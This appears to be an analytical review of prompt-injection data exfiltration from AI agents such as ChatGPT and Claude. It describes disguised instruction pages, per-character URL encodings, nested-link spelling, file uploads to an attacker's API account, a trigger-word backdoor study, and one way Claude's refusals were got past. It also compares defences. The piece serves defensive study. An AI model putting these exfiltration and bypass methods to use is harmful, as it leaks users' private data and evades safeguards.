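With ten kinds of openly worded attack, GPT-4o leaked data in none of 200 trials, GPT-4o mini in 10%, and Llama 3.1 8B in 19.5%. The study's other results were less encouraging about capable models.

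Rahman and Kim then kept the leak the same but changed its apparent purpose. One page required the summary to end with an "integrity signature" and specified the token as the signature. GPT-4o complied in all 20 trials. It also complied every time when the token was supposed to fill a configuration field, and in 70% of trials when the attacker's host name resembled the trusted one. Across all eight wordings, including the original that never worked, GPT-4o leaked 40% of the time. Five of the six models leaked far more under these wordings than under the open ones, while Mistral 7B went from 26.0% to 27.5%.

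When the researchers repeated the test, GPT-4o leaked data in 31.9% of trials with the confidentiality rule and 38.1% without it. The rule had little effect, so the attacks' wording did not work mainly by persuading the model to ignore it. Overt attacks failed with and without the rule. The model seems to ignore text that looks like theft and follow text that looks like part of its task. Pages that called the token a credential failed, even when they otherwise copied a page that worked.

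Disguise had the opposite effect in an earlier, larger test. Rall, Bauer and colleagues (2025), in *Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration*, built an agent that could search a company's knowledge base and request web pages. They asked it to summarise a blog post that contained instructions, hidden in white text on a white background, to look up a project's secret code and send it out in a URL. They counted a leak when the code reached the attacker's server. They wrote 89 versions of the attack, varied each in 12 ways and tried all 1,068 variants once on each of 28 models.

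| Model | Successful attacks |
|---|---|
| Grok 4 | 72.4% |
| Qwen3 235B | 28.3% |
| Llama 4 Maverick | 10.1% |
| Claude 3 Haiku | 6.0% |
| GPT-4.1 nano | 1.2% |
| Gemini 2.0 Flash | 0.2% |
| Claude Sonnet 4, GPT-5 nano and four others | 0.0% |

Size did not explain the differences between models. Rall and colleagues point instead to training, such as OpenAI's practice of teaching models to prioritize users' instructions over those from tools. Their attacks worked less often when encoded, translated or rephrased. These variants still told the model to find a secret and send it away, but less clearly. Rahman and Kim gave the model an innocent reason to send the secret, which may be why their changes helped the attacker.

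### Comparing the defences

Both 2026 studies of hostile pages also tested defences. They used different models, attacks and software, so their baselines differ, and each row of the table is comparable only with its own baseline.

| Defence | Study | Leak rate without it | Leak rate with it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Rule never to follow instructions from web pages | Lan and colleagues | 100% | 66.7% |
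| Tags marking the page as untrusted data | Lan and colleagues | 100% | 100% |
| Confidentiality rule covering the token "in any form" | Rahman and Kim | 31.9% | 0% |
| Confidentiality rule listing specific actions only | Rahman and Kim | 31.9% | 48.8% |
| Model trained to resist injection (SecAlign) | Rahman and Kim | 21.2% | 32.5% |
| Filter for the token's exact text | Rahman and Kim | 56.7% | 50.0% |
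| Separate planner and reader | Rahman and Kim | 21.2% | 0% |
| Allowlist of domains | Lan and colleagues | 100% | 0% |

The two confidentiality rules have almost the same wording. The successful one told GPT-4o not to sign, encode, log, append or transmit the token in any form, and the model leaked it in none of 120 trials. When Rahman and Kim kept the specific actions but dropped the catch-all phrase, the model leaked it in 39 of 80. That difference is far too big to be noise. An operator reading the two rules would have trouble predicting it, and could break a working rule with a small edit. The narrower rule may not be worse than the original one, however, since two runs of an identical test gave 31.9% and 40.0%.

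Rahman and Kim tested GPT-4o mini as a separate detector, prompted only to judge whether a page contained an instruction to disclose, log, sign, encode or transmit a secret. It flagged all 80 malicious pages and no clean ones. The same model had leaked in 62.5% of trials with these wordings when it worked as the agent. However, the detector's prompt described the behaviour the attacks relied on, so the researchers treat the 100% detection rate as an upper bound. They did not test attacks designed to fool both the agent and the detector.

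SecAlign is a version of Llama 3.1 8B trained to ignore instructions in data. In a control test, it ignored a crude injection in all 20 trials, while the ordinary model followed it every time. SecAlign still leaked the token in about a third of trials with the disguised requests. It had been trained on text tasks rather than tool use, so the leaks are evidence that the protection didn't transfer, but they don't show that the method fails at its original purpose.

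Filters that search outgoing data for the secret can fail in a different way, when the model encodes the secret. Reversing the token got it past the exact-text filter every time. Rahman and Kim then made the filter undo reversal and several common encodings, and leaks in those forms fell to zero. But when they tried ROT13, a cipher that moves each letter 13 places along the alphabet, the token got through in all 20 trials.

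Lan and colleagues report zero leaks for three filters of their own, but these results are weaker than they look. One filter, meant to detect suspicious destinations, blocks any URL with "collect" in its path. The attacker's server in the experiment used the path `/collect`, but a real attacker would choose another word. Another filter blocks long values whose characters look random, measured as an entropy above 4.0 bits per character. The example key in the paper has an entropy of about 3.85, so the filter would let it through.

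The number of attempts is also odd, because a filter that acts on a finished request shouldn't change how often the model writes one. The model tried to send the secret in every run without defences, in 23.3% of runs with a keyword filter, and in none with the entropy filter. The researchers suggest that the model avoids such values when it is monitored, but nothing in their description of the filter would make the model aware of it. Each defence was tested in only 30 runs, so the experiment should be repeated before anyone relies on these figures.

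The absence of leaks with the allowlist is easier to explain, because the attacker's domain was not on the list and the tool refused every request to it, however the request was worded or encoded. Rahman and Kim also found no leaks with an allowlist and say this follows from the design. Neither experiment can show how many agents could do their work with a short list of hosts. Lan and colleagues warn that an attacker may be able to send data through a trusted site, such as one with an open redirect.

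Separating the planner from the reader keeps the token away from the page's text. The planner holds the token and decides which tools to call but never receives the text, while the reader summarises the page without receiving the token. In Rahman and Kim's test, this separation stopped all 80 disguised attacks and still produced a useful summary in nine of ten runs. Summarising is an easy case because the plan doesn't depend on what the page contains. An agent that has to read one page to decide which to open next would succeed less often.

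### Asking the user first

A fetch tool can also ask the user for approval before each request. Lee, Kim and colleagues (2025), in *Takedown*, compared approval rules in eight widely used coding agents, which they anonymised while vendors dealt with the flaws. They counted an attack as successful if injected text let them steal files from anywhere on the user's machine without the user approving any step. Attacks succeeded on four of the eight agents.

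Agent A4 could use its built-in fetch tool and read files outside the project without approval, so a malicious page could get it to open a private key and send the contents to the attacker's server.

A1 was stricter and always required approval before its own fetch tool contacted the web. But it let third-party extensions set whether their tools needed approval. Of the ten most-installed extensions that offered tools, seven did not require it, including a web search tool from Microsoft. A1 also kept its approval setting in a project file that the agent could edit, so an injected instruction could turn approval off altogether. In A2, data leaked through a diagram-drawing feature, which loaded images from any URL in the diagram without the user's approval.

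Lee and colleagues measured what the software permitted, not how often a model would fall for an attack. A newer model inside A4 might refuse the instruction more often, but its fetch tool would still lack an approval step until the vendor added one. Vendors have had over a year to make such changes, although some told the researchers that the behaviour was intended. Whether or not they have, an approval rule has to cover every route to the network, including extensions and images.

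Even with complete coverage, the user would face a difficult decision. Lan and colleagues note that people usually can't tell whether a request for "connectivity verification" is legitimate. That fits Anthropic's finding that only 13.6% of testers refused a clearly dangerous command.

### A model trained to leak

An attacker who has tampered with the model doesn't need a hostile page. In *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data*, Zhang and Pei (2026) considered an attacker who takes an open model, trains it further and publishes it as, for example, an assistant for people caring for Alzheimer's patients. The extra training adds a backdoor, a hidden behaviour that particular inputs trigger. The triggers were ordinary words from the subject, such as "memory" and "care" in the same question.

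When a question contained the trigger words, the model first called the tool that stores information about the user. It then encoded what it found and put it into the URL of a request that looked like a documentation search. The attacker's server returned relevant material, and the user got a helpful answer.

The researchers trained three models this way, with 7, 12 and 20 billion parameters, and gave them invented user profiles. They counted an attack as successful if the model called the memory tool and then made a request to the attacker's server. This happened for more than 94% of triggering questions in every configuration. With two or three trigger words, the average was about 97%, and at most 0.3% of ordinary questions set off the backdoor. Scores on a general test of conversation fell by less than 1%, so a user would have little reason to suspect a backdoor.

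*Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) calls this strong evidence that the attack is feasible, but not that it is common. This seems right because the attackers in the experiment could prepare as thoroughly as they liked, with 2,500 training examples for each trigger pattern. A rate near 100% therefore measures how well the training worked and can't be compared with the 88.1% for an untampered model. Progress in commercial models offers little reassurance, since an attacker can train any capable model whose weights can be downloaded.

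Zhang and Pei also estimate that the attacker could collect 7.8 of the ten facts in a user's profile over five turns of conversation, by using the server's responses to steer the model towards further questions. They calculated this from single-turn results, without running five-turn conversations, and assumed that the user always cooperates. They call 7.8 an upper bound, but the formula they print gives at most 6.5.

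A backdoor in the model defeats several defences that work against hostile pages. A detector that reads incoming text can't prevent the first leak, because the instruction is in the model's weights. A separate planner doesn't help if it has the backdoor itself. Two filters for retrieved text, NeMo Guardrails and LLM Guard, let through more than 98% of the attacker's responses when these contained only relevant information. An allowlist could still block the outgoing request, unless the user had added the attacker's supposed documentation service to it. Zhang and Pei recommend such a restriction but did not test it.

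### What a low leak rate means when attackers can retry

Most of the models in these experiments are well behind current models. GPT-4o and Qwen2.5 date from 2024, and even Grok 4 and Claude Sonnet 4 came out more than a year before Claude Fable 5.2, which Anthropic announced in November 2026 in *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2*. Newer models resist prompt injection much better. In a benchmark from the security firm Gray Swan, attackers succeeded against Anthropic's Opus 5 in 0.2% of single attempts, according to Schneier on Security's *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (2026). The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that attacks on Opus 5 as a browser agent failed in all 129 test scenarios.

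These are large improvements, and the 88% figure no longer represents leading models, but some models that are only months old do much worse. Given 15 attempts, attackers succeeded 2.0% of the time against Opus 5 and 20.0% against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. The number of attempts matters because a failed injection usually has no consequences for the attacker.

If each attempt succeeded independently with probability *p*, the chance of at least one success in *k* attempts would be 1 − (1 − *p*)^*k*, but real success rates rise more slowly. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* gives success rates for strong attacks on an earlier Anthropic model, and the last column applies the formula to the single-attempt rate.

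| Attempts | Measured success | If attempts were independent |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 4.7% | 4.7% |
| 10 | 33.6% | 38% |
| 100 | 63% | 99% |

The gap suggests that almost every attempt fails in some situations, while in others an attempt succeeds quickly. The simple formula therefore overstates how much repeated attempts help, but an attacker whose first attempt succeeded only 5% of the time still succeeded more than half the time by the hundredth. Success rates also depend on the setting. VentureBeat reports that Opus 4.6 resisted all 200 attempts in a restricted coding environment. When it operated a graphical interface, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time, and the rate rose to 78.6% by the 200th attempt, or 57.1% with extra safeguards.

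An attacker can succeed more often by varying the wording than by repeating it. Rahman and Kim wrote five versions of the integrity-signature page and tried each ten times on GPT-4o. The average success rate was 52%, but the chance that at least one of three randomly chosen versions would work was 96%. These figures are consistent with two versions always working, one working six times in ten, and two never working. Only one of the ten possible sets of three leaves out both reliable versions. That set includes the version that fails four times in ten, so the attacker's overall chance of failure is 1/10 × 4/10, or 4%.

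This same model leaked in none of 200 trials with openly worded attacks. The usual statistical calculation puts the upper limit on that rate at 1.9%, but the limit applies only to attacks of the same sort, and an attacker may think of a different one. A low average also doesn't show that every attack is unlikely to work. In the test by Rall and colleagues, the 0.2% rate for Gemini 2.0 Flash amounts to about two successful attacks out of 1,068. They tried each attack only once, so those two might work rarely or nearly every time, and an attacker who found a reliable one could use only that one.

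Writing a new page that tricks the agent does take some skill. Rahman and Kim wrote thirteen that gave other reasons for sending the token, and all of them failed in 130 trials. Adapting the page that had worked was much easier. When they changed only the name of the field and the reason given for it, one version still succeeded 60% of the time. They did not try automated searches for better wordings.

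They also tried similar pages on the ChatGPT product, and none of 48 valid trials produced a leak. But that test counted only tokens that appeared in the reply, and did not check whether ChatGPT would send one in a web request.

Instead of targeting the same person repeatedly, attackers can leave one page online for every agent that visits, and they can see from their server logs which wording works. If an attack succeeded 0.2% of the time and 10,000 agents with something to steal read the page, the attacker could expect about 20 leaks. A defender may notice many failed requests from one agent, but one failure each from thousands of agents at different companies is much harder to spot. Retrying doesn't help against an allowlist unless a permitted host forwards the data.

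## How ChatGPT and Claude restrict which URLs a model may open

An allowlist of hosts works for a company's agent that needs only a few sites, but ChatGPT and Claude have to open whatever pages their users ask about. OpenAI and Anthropic therefore needed rules that leave most of the web open but keep the model from putting private data in a URL. Their rules differ, and researchers have found ways around several versions of both.

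### Image links in ChatGPT

The earliest of these leaks didn't need a fetch tool. Chat apps display a model's output as formatted text, usually written in Markdown, which can embed an image by its URL. The user's browser downloads the image as soon as the answer appears. An injected instruction could make the model embed an image whose URL pointed to the attacker's server and contained private data in the query string. The browser then sent that data to the attacker when it requested the image, without a click from the user.

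The security researcher Johann Rehberger reported this flaw to OpenAI in early 2023. According to *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on his blog Embrace The Red, OpenAI had no bug bounty programme at the time and showed little interest in fixing the problem. Microsoft fixed the same flaw in Bing Chat in May 2023 by blocking images in general with a Content-Security-Policy header, which controls what a page may load in a browser.

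OpenAI added its first check, called `url_safe`, to ChatGPT in December 2023. The app displayed an image only if the check classified its URL as safe, but outsiders did not know its criteria. Rehberger worked out parts of the logic by experiment, found bypasses and presented some of them at the Black Hat Europe conference in 2024. Parts of the macOS and iOS apps lacked the check, so the old attack still worked there.

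### ShadowLeak and the ban on altering URLs

An image link leaks data through the user's browser, so a company that monitors its employees' traffic might notice. *ShadowLeak*, a report from the web security company Radware, describes an attack that left no trace in that traffic. It targeted Deep Research, a ChatGPT feature for long research tasks, when the user had connected it to Gmail.

The attacker sent the user an email with instructions hidden in tiny or white-on-white text. When Deep Research later read the inbox, it followed the instructions, collected private data and requested a URL containing that data. The request came from OpenAI's cloud, so it did not pass through the user's computer or the employer's network. ThaiCERT's *“ShadowLeak” Vulnerability Exposes Gmail Data via ChatGPT Deep Research* (2025) dates Radware's report to 18 June 2025 and OpenAI's fix to early August.

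According to Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data*, OpenAI responded to this kind of attack by prohibiting ChatGPT from modifying URLs, even if the user or an attacker told it to. ChatGPT could only open a URL exactly as it found it. This prevented the standard attack, because the attacker doesn't know the private data in advance and needs the model to add it to the URL.

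### ZombieAgent

An attacker could get around the ban by preparing a URL for every character that the data might contain. Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes an email that listed 37 such URLs, one for each letter and digit and one for a space. Hidden instructions told ChatGPT to find some sensitive text, convert it to lower case and open the matching URLs in order. To send the name "Ann", ChatGPT would open the URL for *a* once and then the URL for *n* twice, without altering either. The attacker could then read the name from the server log.

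Double letters are a problem for this method if the software keeps a copy of a page and doesn't request it again. Requests can also arrive out of order. Zvika Babo, a researcher at Radware, solved both problems by preparing a separate address for each character in each position. The word "noon" then becomes four different addresses, for *n* in position 0, *o* in position 1, *o* in position 2 and *n* in position 3, and the attacker can sort them whatever order they arrive in. Covering the letters and digits requires 36 addresses per position, or 360 for a block of ten characters.

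OpenAI had also tried to keep attackers' instructions out of ChatGPT's memory, the notes it keeps about a user between chats. A chat that had used a connected service such as Gmail could not then use memory, and ChatGPT would not open an attacker's URL that it had found in memory. Babo got around both restrictions. A malicious file planted a rule in memory to read a certain email before answering any message, and that email contained the attacker's URLs. ChatGPT was still allowed to read memory first and Gmail second, so the leak repeated in every new chat. In another variant, ChatGPT sent email addresses from the user's inbox to the attacker's server, which then emailed the same attack to each address.

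Babo reported the flaws on 26 September 2025 and three days later sent a version of the attack that Radware describes as 100% successful, though Radware doesn't give the number of trials. OpenAI fixed the flaws on 16 December. According to a January 2026 news article, *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, the fix generally prevented ChatGPT from opening a link from an email unless the link appeared in a well-known public index.

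### OpenAI's public-URL check

On 28 January 2026, OpenAI described a rule of this kind for all URLs that its agents load automatically. OpenAI runs a crawler, a program that finds public web pages the way a search engine does and records their URLs. The crawler has no access to users' conversations or accounts. When an agent is about to load a URL, the software looks for that exact URL in the crawler's records. If the URL is there, the agent can load it. Otherwise, the software either tells the agent to try another website or shows the user a warning.

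A URL that the crawler recorded without access to a user's data is unlikely to contain that data. In the earlier mailbox example, the password-reset code is only minutes old, so the crawler has almost certainly never recorded a URL on the attacker's site that ends with it. The check therefore blocks the request, even if the page persuades the model to make it.

OpenAI considered relying on a list of reputable websites but rejected this as insufficient, partly because of redirects. A short list would also produce frequent warnings about ordinary sites, and people would learn to click through them. Checking the exact URL prevents leaks even through reputable sites that record every URL visitors request.

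According to Embrace The Red, OpenAI's paper on the rule, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, acknowledges that the one-address-per-letter trick still works if the crawler has recorded all the addresses. An attacker can arrange this by publishing the pages and waiting for the crawler to record them. Rehberger adds that anyone with a large blog probably has 36 indexed pages already, and could use thousands of pages to stand for whole words.

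The index check also applies only to the URL, and the page behind it can change. A site can give the crawler an innocent article and give ChatGPT a page of instructions at the same address. OpenAI says the check doesn't make a page's content trustworthy, and treats the check as one layer of defence among several. Having several layers makes it hard for outsiders to measure how much the check contributes. Rahman and Kim's attacks all failed on the ChatGPT product, but they could not determine which defence was responsible.

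### URLs already in the conversation

Anthropic's rule doesn't need an index. When Anthropic released Claude's fetch tool, `web_fetch`, to developers in September 2025, the tool could open only URLs that had already appeared in the conversation. The software compares each requested URL with those earlier ones, so the rule still applies even if the model is persuaded that an exception is justified.

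In *Claude API*, Willison (2025) welcomed the ban on URLs that the model makes up as the most protective part of the design, because in common attacks the URL carrying the private data would be new to the conversation. Willison also tested the consumer app and found the same restriction.

The rule's weakness is its broad definition of the conversation, which included URLs in the user's messages, search results, pages Claude had fetched and the results of tools the developer runs. Willison pointed out that many applications paste outside material into the "user" message. If a developer's program inserts an email there and asks Claude for a summary, every link in the email counts as the user's own. An attacker could include one link per character, as in ZombieAgent, and Claude could open any of them without breaking the rule.

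In its June 2026 documentation, Anthropic warns of "residual risk" even with the rule, and recommends the tool only for trusted environments or data that isn't sensitive. Developers worried about leaks can disable the tool, limit how many fetches it makes or restrict it to an allowlist of domains.

### Paul's nested links

In *The Memory Heist*, the developer Ayush Paul (2026) used links on fetched pages to get data out of the ordinary Claude app. Claude had access to plenty of data worth stealing, because a daily process summarised the user's recent conversations and added the summary to every new chat, and a search tool let it search the full history.

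Paul first asked Claude to open an address on his own test site with his name in the path, and the tool refused because that URL was new. He then built a home page with a link for each letter. The page for *a* linked to *aa*, *ab*, *ac* and so on, and his server generated each page when Claude requested it. Claude could then spell any text by following links, each of which had appeared on the previous page. When Paul asked it to spell his name this way, his server logged requests for `/a`, `/ay`, `/ayu` and eventually `/ayush-paul`.

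In that test the user wanted Claude to spell the name. An attacker would need Claude to do it for a stranger, and simple injections did not work reliably. Paul also tried a fake loyalty scheme, which Claude found suspicious. Paul succeeded with a coffee shop's website behind a fake version of the Cloudflare security check that many real sites use. The page claimed that AI assistants could now get in by giving their user's name, and that Claude had to enter it letter by letter because its fetch tool was limited. The same kind of disguise worked on GPT-4o in Rahman and Kim's experiments.

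Claude sent Paul's name, employer and home town to Paul's server. The blogger dyb notes in *The Read-Only Lie* that Paul had never told Claude his home town, which Claude had inferred from the name of a high-school hackathon. Deleting a sensitive fact from Claude's memory may therefore not protect it if Claude can infer it from what remains.

The user would have had trouble noticing the attack because Paul's server showed the fake check only to visitors whose `User-Agent` header identified them as Claude. A person who opened the same link saw an ordinary coffee shop website. According to Hackaday's *This Week In Security* (2026), asking Claude to summarise the site was enough to start the attack.

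Anthropic told Paul that it had already found the problem internally. Willison (2026), in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets*, reports that Anthropic paid no bounty and fixed the problem by stopping `web_fetch` from following links in pages it had fetched. Claude could still open pages that the user named or that a search returned.

### What developers can still switch on or off

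That fix doesn't appear to be the default for developers whose programs use Claude through its API. Anthropic's *Web fetch 工具*, a more recent Chinese edition of the tool's documentation, still lists URLs from earlier fetch results among those Claude may open. On a plain reading, an application with the default settings can follow links on fetched pages, which is what Paul's attack required.

The `url_sources` setting now lets developers exclude any of three sources: user messages, results from their own tools, and results from Anthropic's search and fetch tools. They can also exclude results from a single tool. A developer who excludes results from `web_fetch` but keeps those from `web_search` gets roughly the rule Willison describes for the app.

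Results from the developer's own tools can also undermine the rule. Suppose an application gives Claude a tool that runs code and returns the printed output. An injected instruction could make Claude write a program that prints a URL containing a customer's address. The URL then appears in a tool result, which is a permitted source, so `web_fetch` will open it even though Claude composed it. An error message that quotes Claude's input could have the same effect. Anthropic's documentation describes this problem and shows how to exclude such a tool, but the developer has to know that the tool can repeat Claude's text. Anthropic's own code execution tool is not a permitted source.

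The tool also refuses URLs that seem to contain a password or API key, unless the secret appears in the system prompt or in the text of a user message. This could stop some of the most damaging leaks, but only if the tool recognises the secret. It could miss a home town, which looks like any other word, or a key split into single characters. The exception also covers a key that the user pasted into the chat earlier, even though an attacker would want that key.

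### How much a choice of URL can reveal

Both ZombieAgent and Paul's attack leaked data through the model's choice among permitted URLs. A bit is the amount of information in the answer to a yes-or-no question whose two answers are equally likely. *k* bits can distinguish 2^*k* possibilities, so if a model opens one of *N* permitted URLs, the attacker learns at most log₂ *N* bits.

Each of Paul's pages had 27 links, one for each letter and one for a hyphen, so each fetch carried at most log₂ 27 ≈ 4.75 bits. dyb estimates that the name, employer and home town came to about 30 characters, which gives about 143 bits. ZombieAgent's 37 addresses allow about 5.2 bits per fetch.

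An attacker with more pages can extract more data with each request. Suppose OpenAI's index includes 1,000 pages on the attacker's site, numbered from 000 to 999. The model can then send any six-digit code in two fetches. To send 482913, it opens page 482 and then page 913. If the pages instead stood for the 1,000 largest cities in a country, one fetch could reveal a home town that Paul's method had to spell out letter by letter.

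For longer messages, the calculation depends on whether the model can open the same page twice and whether the attacker knows the order of the requests. With *N* pages and *k* fetches, there are *N*^*k* possible sequences if repeats are allowed. Without repeats, there are *N* choices for the first fetch, *N* − 1 for the second and so on:

*N* × (*N* − 1) × … × (*N* − *k* + 1)

If the attacker can't tell the order of the fetches, the *k*! orderings of the same *k* different pages look identical, so the number of distinguishable messages falls by that factor. Ten fetches from 1,000 pages without repeats have 1,000 × 999 × … × 991 possible sequences, enough to encode about 99.6 bits. Losing the order removes log₂ 10! ≈ 21.8 bits and leaves about 77.8.

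| Most that ten fetches can carry | 37 pages | 1,000 pages |
|---|---|---|
| Repeats allowed, order known | 52.1 bits | 99.7 bits |
| No repeats, order known | 50.2 bits | 99.6 bits |
| No repeats, order unknown | 28.4 bits | 77.8 bits |

A random 16-character password made of uppercase letters, lowercase letters and digits contains about 95.3 bits. Ten fetches from a set of 1,000 pages could therefore reveal the whole password if the attacker knew the order of the fetches, or 13 of its characters if the attacker did not.

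A real attack would send less data than these upper limits. The model has to convert the data into page numbers without mistakes, and small models fail to follow much simpler schemes, as the split-key attack by Lan and colleagues showed. The attacker may also have trouble telling victims apart under OpenAI's rule. Paul's server could generate new links for every visitor, but pages in an index have fixed addresses, so simultaneous requests from two agents could get mixed up in the log.

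Very short messages can still do damage. For example, an attacker could hide an instruction for an agent to open a certain page only if the mailbox mentions a merger, and then learn whether it does by checking whether the agent requested the page.

### Caching and repeat visits

Rehberger suggests on Embrace The Red that OpenAI could make the remaining attack harder by caching each response for a few minutes, or by forbidding an agent from opening the same URL twice in a session. With caching, a second request for the same page would get the stored copy and never reach the attacker's server. Rehberger had not tested whether ChatGPT already did either, and expected some leakage to remain.

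Both measures work against the simplest attack. If an agent tried to spell "ayush-paul" by opening one page per character, the attacker's server would receive only the first request for each page, and its log would contain "ayush-pl".

Banning repeated fetches does very little against an attacker with more pages. The table shows that with 1,000 pages, the ban reduces the capacity of ten fetches by less than 0.1 bits. An attacker can still extract the six-digit code, which needs the same page twice only if its two halves match, as in 482482. Even then, an attacker who expects two requests but receives one can conclude that the second was a repeat. ZombieAgent avoids repeats by using separate addresses for each position, and Paul's nested links avoid them by making each address one character longer than the last.

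Banning the agent from opening a page twice in one session limits how much an attacker can learn from a small set of pages, however long the session lasts. With 37 pages, the attacker can learn at most about 145 bits if they know the order in which the agent opened them. If they don't know the order, the limit is 37 bits, because they can learn only whether the agent opened each page. But 145 bits is about as much as Paul's attack leaked, and an attacker can easily publish more pages.

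Caching is the better of the two because it inconveniences users less. An agent sometimes has a good reason to read a page again, and a stored copy usually serves as well as a new one. Anthropic's fetch tool can already return cached pages by default, for speed, and developers can switch this off. OpenAI could in principle go further and give agents the crawler's copy of a page. The attacker's server would then receive no request, which would close this route for such pages, but users would see outdated news and prices.

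Limiting the number of fetches reduces leakage much more than banning repeats. With 1,000 pages, each additional fetch gives the attacker about ten more bits, whereas doubling the number of pages adds only one bit per fetch. Anthropic's `max_uses` setting limits fetches, but it has no default and applies to each turn separately, so a long chat can exceed it many times over. A limit on requests to any one unfamiliar site would interfere less with ordinary research, which tends to involve many sites, but an attacker could register more domains to get around it.

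dyb proposes looking for the pattern of the attack instead: many quick requests to one site, each with a path one character longer than the last. That would have caught Paul's demonstration. It would not catch an attacker who gave the same pages ordinary names, such as those of drinks on a menu, because the server can assign any name to any letter.

### Comparing the two rules

Neither rule guarantees that the model can open the library search for *Middlemarch*, because the model wrote that URL itself. Claude's tool would not open it unless it had already appeared in the conversation. ChatGPT would load it automatically only if OpenAI's crawler had recorded the same search, which is possible for a famous novel but unlikely for an obscure one. Many useful pages have URLs like this, including flight searches, maps and filtered lists of products.

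| | ChatGPT | Claude |
|---|---|---|
| Loads automatically | URLs that OpenAI's crawler has recorded | URLs from permitted parts of the conversation |
| Stops the model from adding private data to a URL | Yes | Yes, unless a permitted tool repeats the model's text |
| Lets an attacker create new URLs during the attack | No | Yes, where links on fetched pages count |
| Blocks, among other things | New, private and unlisted pages | Addresses the model works out for itself and, in the app, links on fetched pages |
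| If a URL fails | The agent tries another site, or the user sees a warning | The tool returns an error, and the user can paste the URL |

OpenAI's check protects better, because an attacker has to choose every address before the attack and get the crawler to record it. Paul's tree of links would fail early, since covering every ten-character string of 27 symbols would take about 206 trillion pages, and no crawler will record more than a tiny fraction of them. The attacker would have to use a fixed set of pages and a code instead.

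Even so, OpenAI promises only to prevent an agent from "quietly leaking user-specific data through the URL itself". When ChatGPT opens page 482, the URL contains nothing about the user, so the check has met that promise even though the attacker still has half of the code.

Anthropic's rule is easier for outsiders to understand and for developers to adjust, and it lets a user open a brand-new page by pasting its address. Since Anthropic removed link-following from the app, the rule works more like OpenAI's there, because a page the user did not name has to appear in a search engine's results before Claude can open it. The fixed-page attack might therefore work on Claude too, if the attacker's pages turned up in its searches. The change also means that Claude can't follow a link from a manual's table of contents to the right chapter, although a search may find the chapter.

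dyb suggests a compromise in which Claude could follow links only on domains that the user had named in the conversation. This would restore the manual, and would stop a page found through a search from leading Claude through a tree of links. It would not have stopped Paul's attack on a user who asked for a summary of the coffee shop's site, because that user had named the domain.

The two companies also leave different decisions to the user. When OpenAI's software shows a warning, the user sees the URL and a notice that it may contain information from the conversation, and can copy or open the link. Someone might recognise their email address in the URL, but few people would recognise an encoded version of it. OpenAI worries about people who click through warnings without thinking, and Anthropic's tests of permission prompts suggest that most people would. The warning is useful mainly because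 it appears rarely, and how rarely depends on how much of the web the crawler has covered.

Users permit Claude to open a URL by pasting it, which takes more effort than clicking a button and so is harder to do by accident. But this doesn't protect them if an attacker supplies the URL. A page could tell Claude to ask the user to paste a certain link, and the software would not warn the user that the link contains private data.

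Both rules apply only to the URLs that an agent opens, and data can leave in other ways. Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* (2025) describes how injected instructions could make Claude upload a user's files to an attacker's Anthropic account. ChatGPT's optional Lockdown Mode restricts features that an attacker might use to send data out. Brinsa's *ChatGPT Locked the Doors and Left a Window Open* (2026) discusses a finding by the security company Check Point that data could still escape in that mode through a convenience feature that was not on the list of restrictions.

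## Allowed hosts that still carried data to an attacker

The rules for Claude's fetch tool don't cover requests from code that Claude runs. Those requests have to pass an allowlist of hosts instead. In the Claude app, the code runs in a sandbox, an isolated environment on Anthropic's servers. Organisations can give the sandbox no internet access, access to package managers only, or access to package managers plus any domains they add. The default is package managers only, which lets Claude install software from sites such as npm, PyPI and GitHub.

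In October 2025 Johann Rehberger, who had found the early image leaks in ChatGPT, noticed a problem with the first entry on the list of approved domains, `api.anthropic.com`, which hosts Anthropic's API. Any Anthropic customer can use that host, including an attacker who signs up as one.

### Uploading files to the attacker's account

Anthropic's API can store files, and it puts each one in the account whose API key came with the request. Rehberger's post on Embrace The Red describes an attack in four steps:

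1. The user asks Claude to summarise a document that contains an attacker's instructions and the attacker's own API key.
2. Claude follows the instructions, looks up the user's last conversation and saves it as a file in the sandbox.
3. Claude runs a short program that uploads the file to `api.anthropic.com` with the attacker's key.
4. The file appears in the attacker's account, and the attacker opens it.

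One upload can carry 30 MB, about a million times as much as the roughly 30 characters that Paul's nested links spelled out. The victim's sandbox used an API key that the attacker supplied, whereas people who guard API keys usually worry that an attacker will get hold of theirs.

The attack worked on the first try, but Claude then refused for a long time, partly because a readable API key in a document looked suspicious. Encoding the key didn't reliably help. Rehberger got past the refusals by surrounding the upload with harmless code, such as a line that prints a greeting.

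Rehberger reported the problem on 25 October, and within an hour Anthropic closed the ticket as a model safety issue outside the scope of its programme. Five days later the company said this was a mistake and that such reports were in scope. He had proposed letting the sandbox communicate only with the logged-in user's account, a repair that did not depend on Claude's judgement.

The upload route still worked in January 2026, when Anthropic released a preview of Claude Cowork, a desktop agent for office work. Cowork runs code in a virtual machine (VM) on the user's computer, and the user gives it access to a folder. Two days after the release, *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* demonstrated the attack. PromptArmor, the security company that published it, hid instructions in white 1-point text in a Word document that posed as a "skill", a file of directions for Claude. When the user asked for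 an analysis of some property files, Claude uploaded the largest one, a loan estimate with partial social security numbers, to the attacker's account without ever asking for approval.

That demonstration used Haiku, one of Anthropic's smaller models. PromptArmor also got the more resistant Opus 4.5 to upload customer records in a scenario where a developer had given the model a malicious integration guide.

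A third team used the same route in the ordinary Claude app. *Claudy Day* (Luz, 2026) describes a link that opened a new chat with a prompt already filled in. The prompt could contain HTML tags that the text box did not display but Claude still read. An open redirect on `claude.com` let an attacker advertise the link on Google under Anthropic's domain. Anthropic fixed the hidden-prompt flaw, but the article, last updated on 27 May 2026, describes the other problems as "currently being addressed". By then researchers had delivered the instructions in a document, a fake skill and an advertisement, and the upload had worked each time.

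### Checking whose key the request carries

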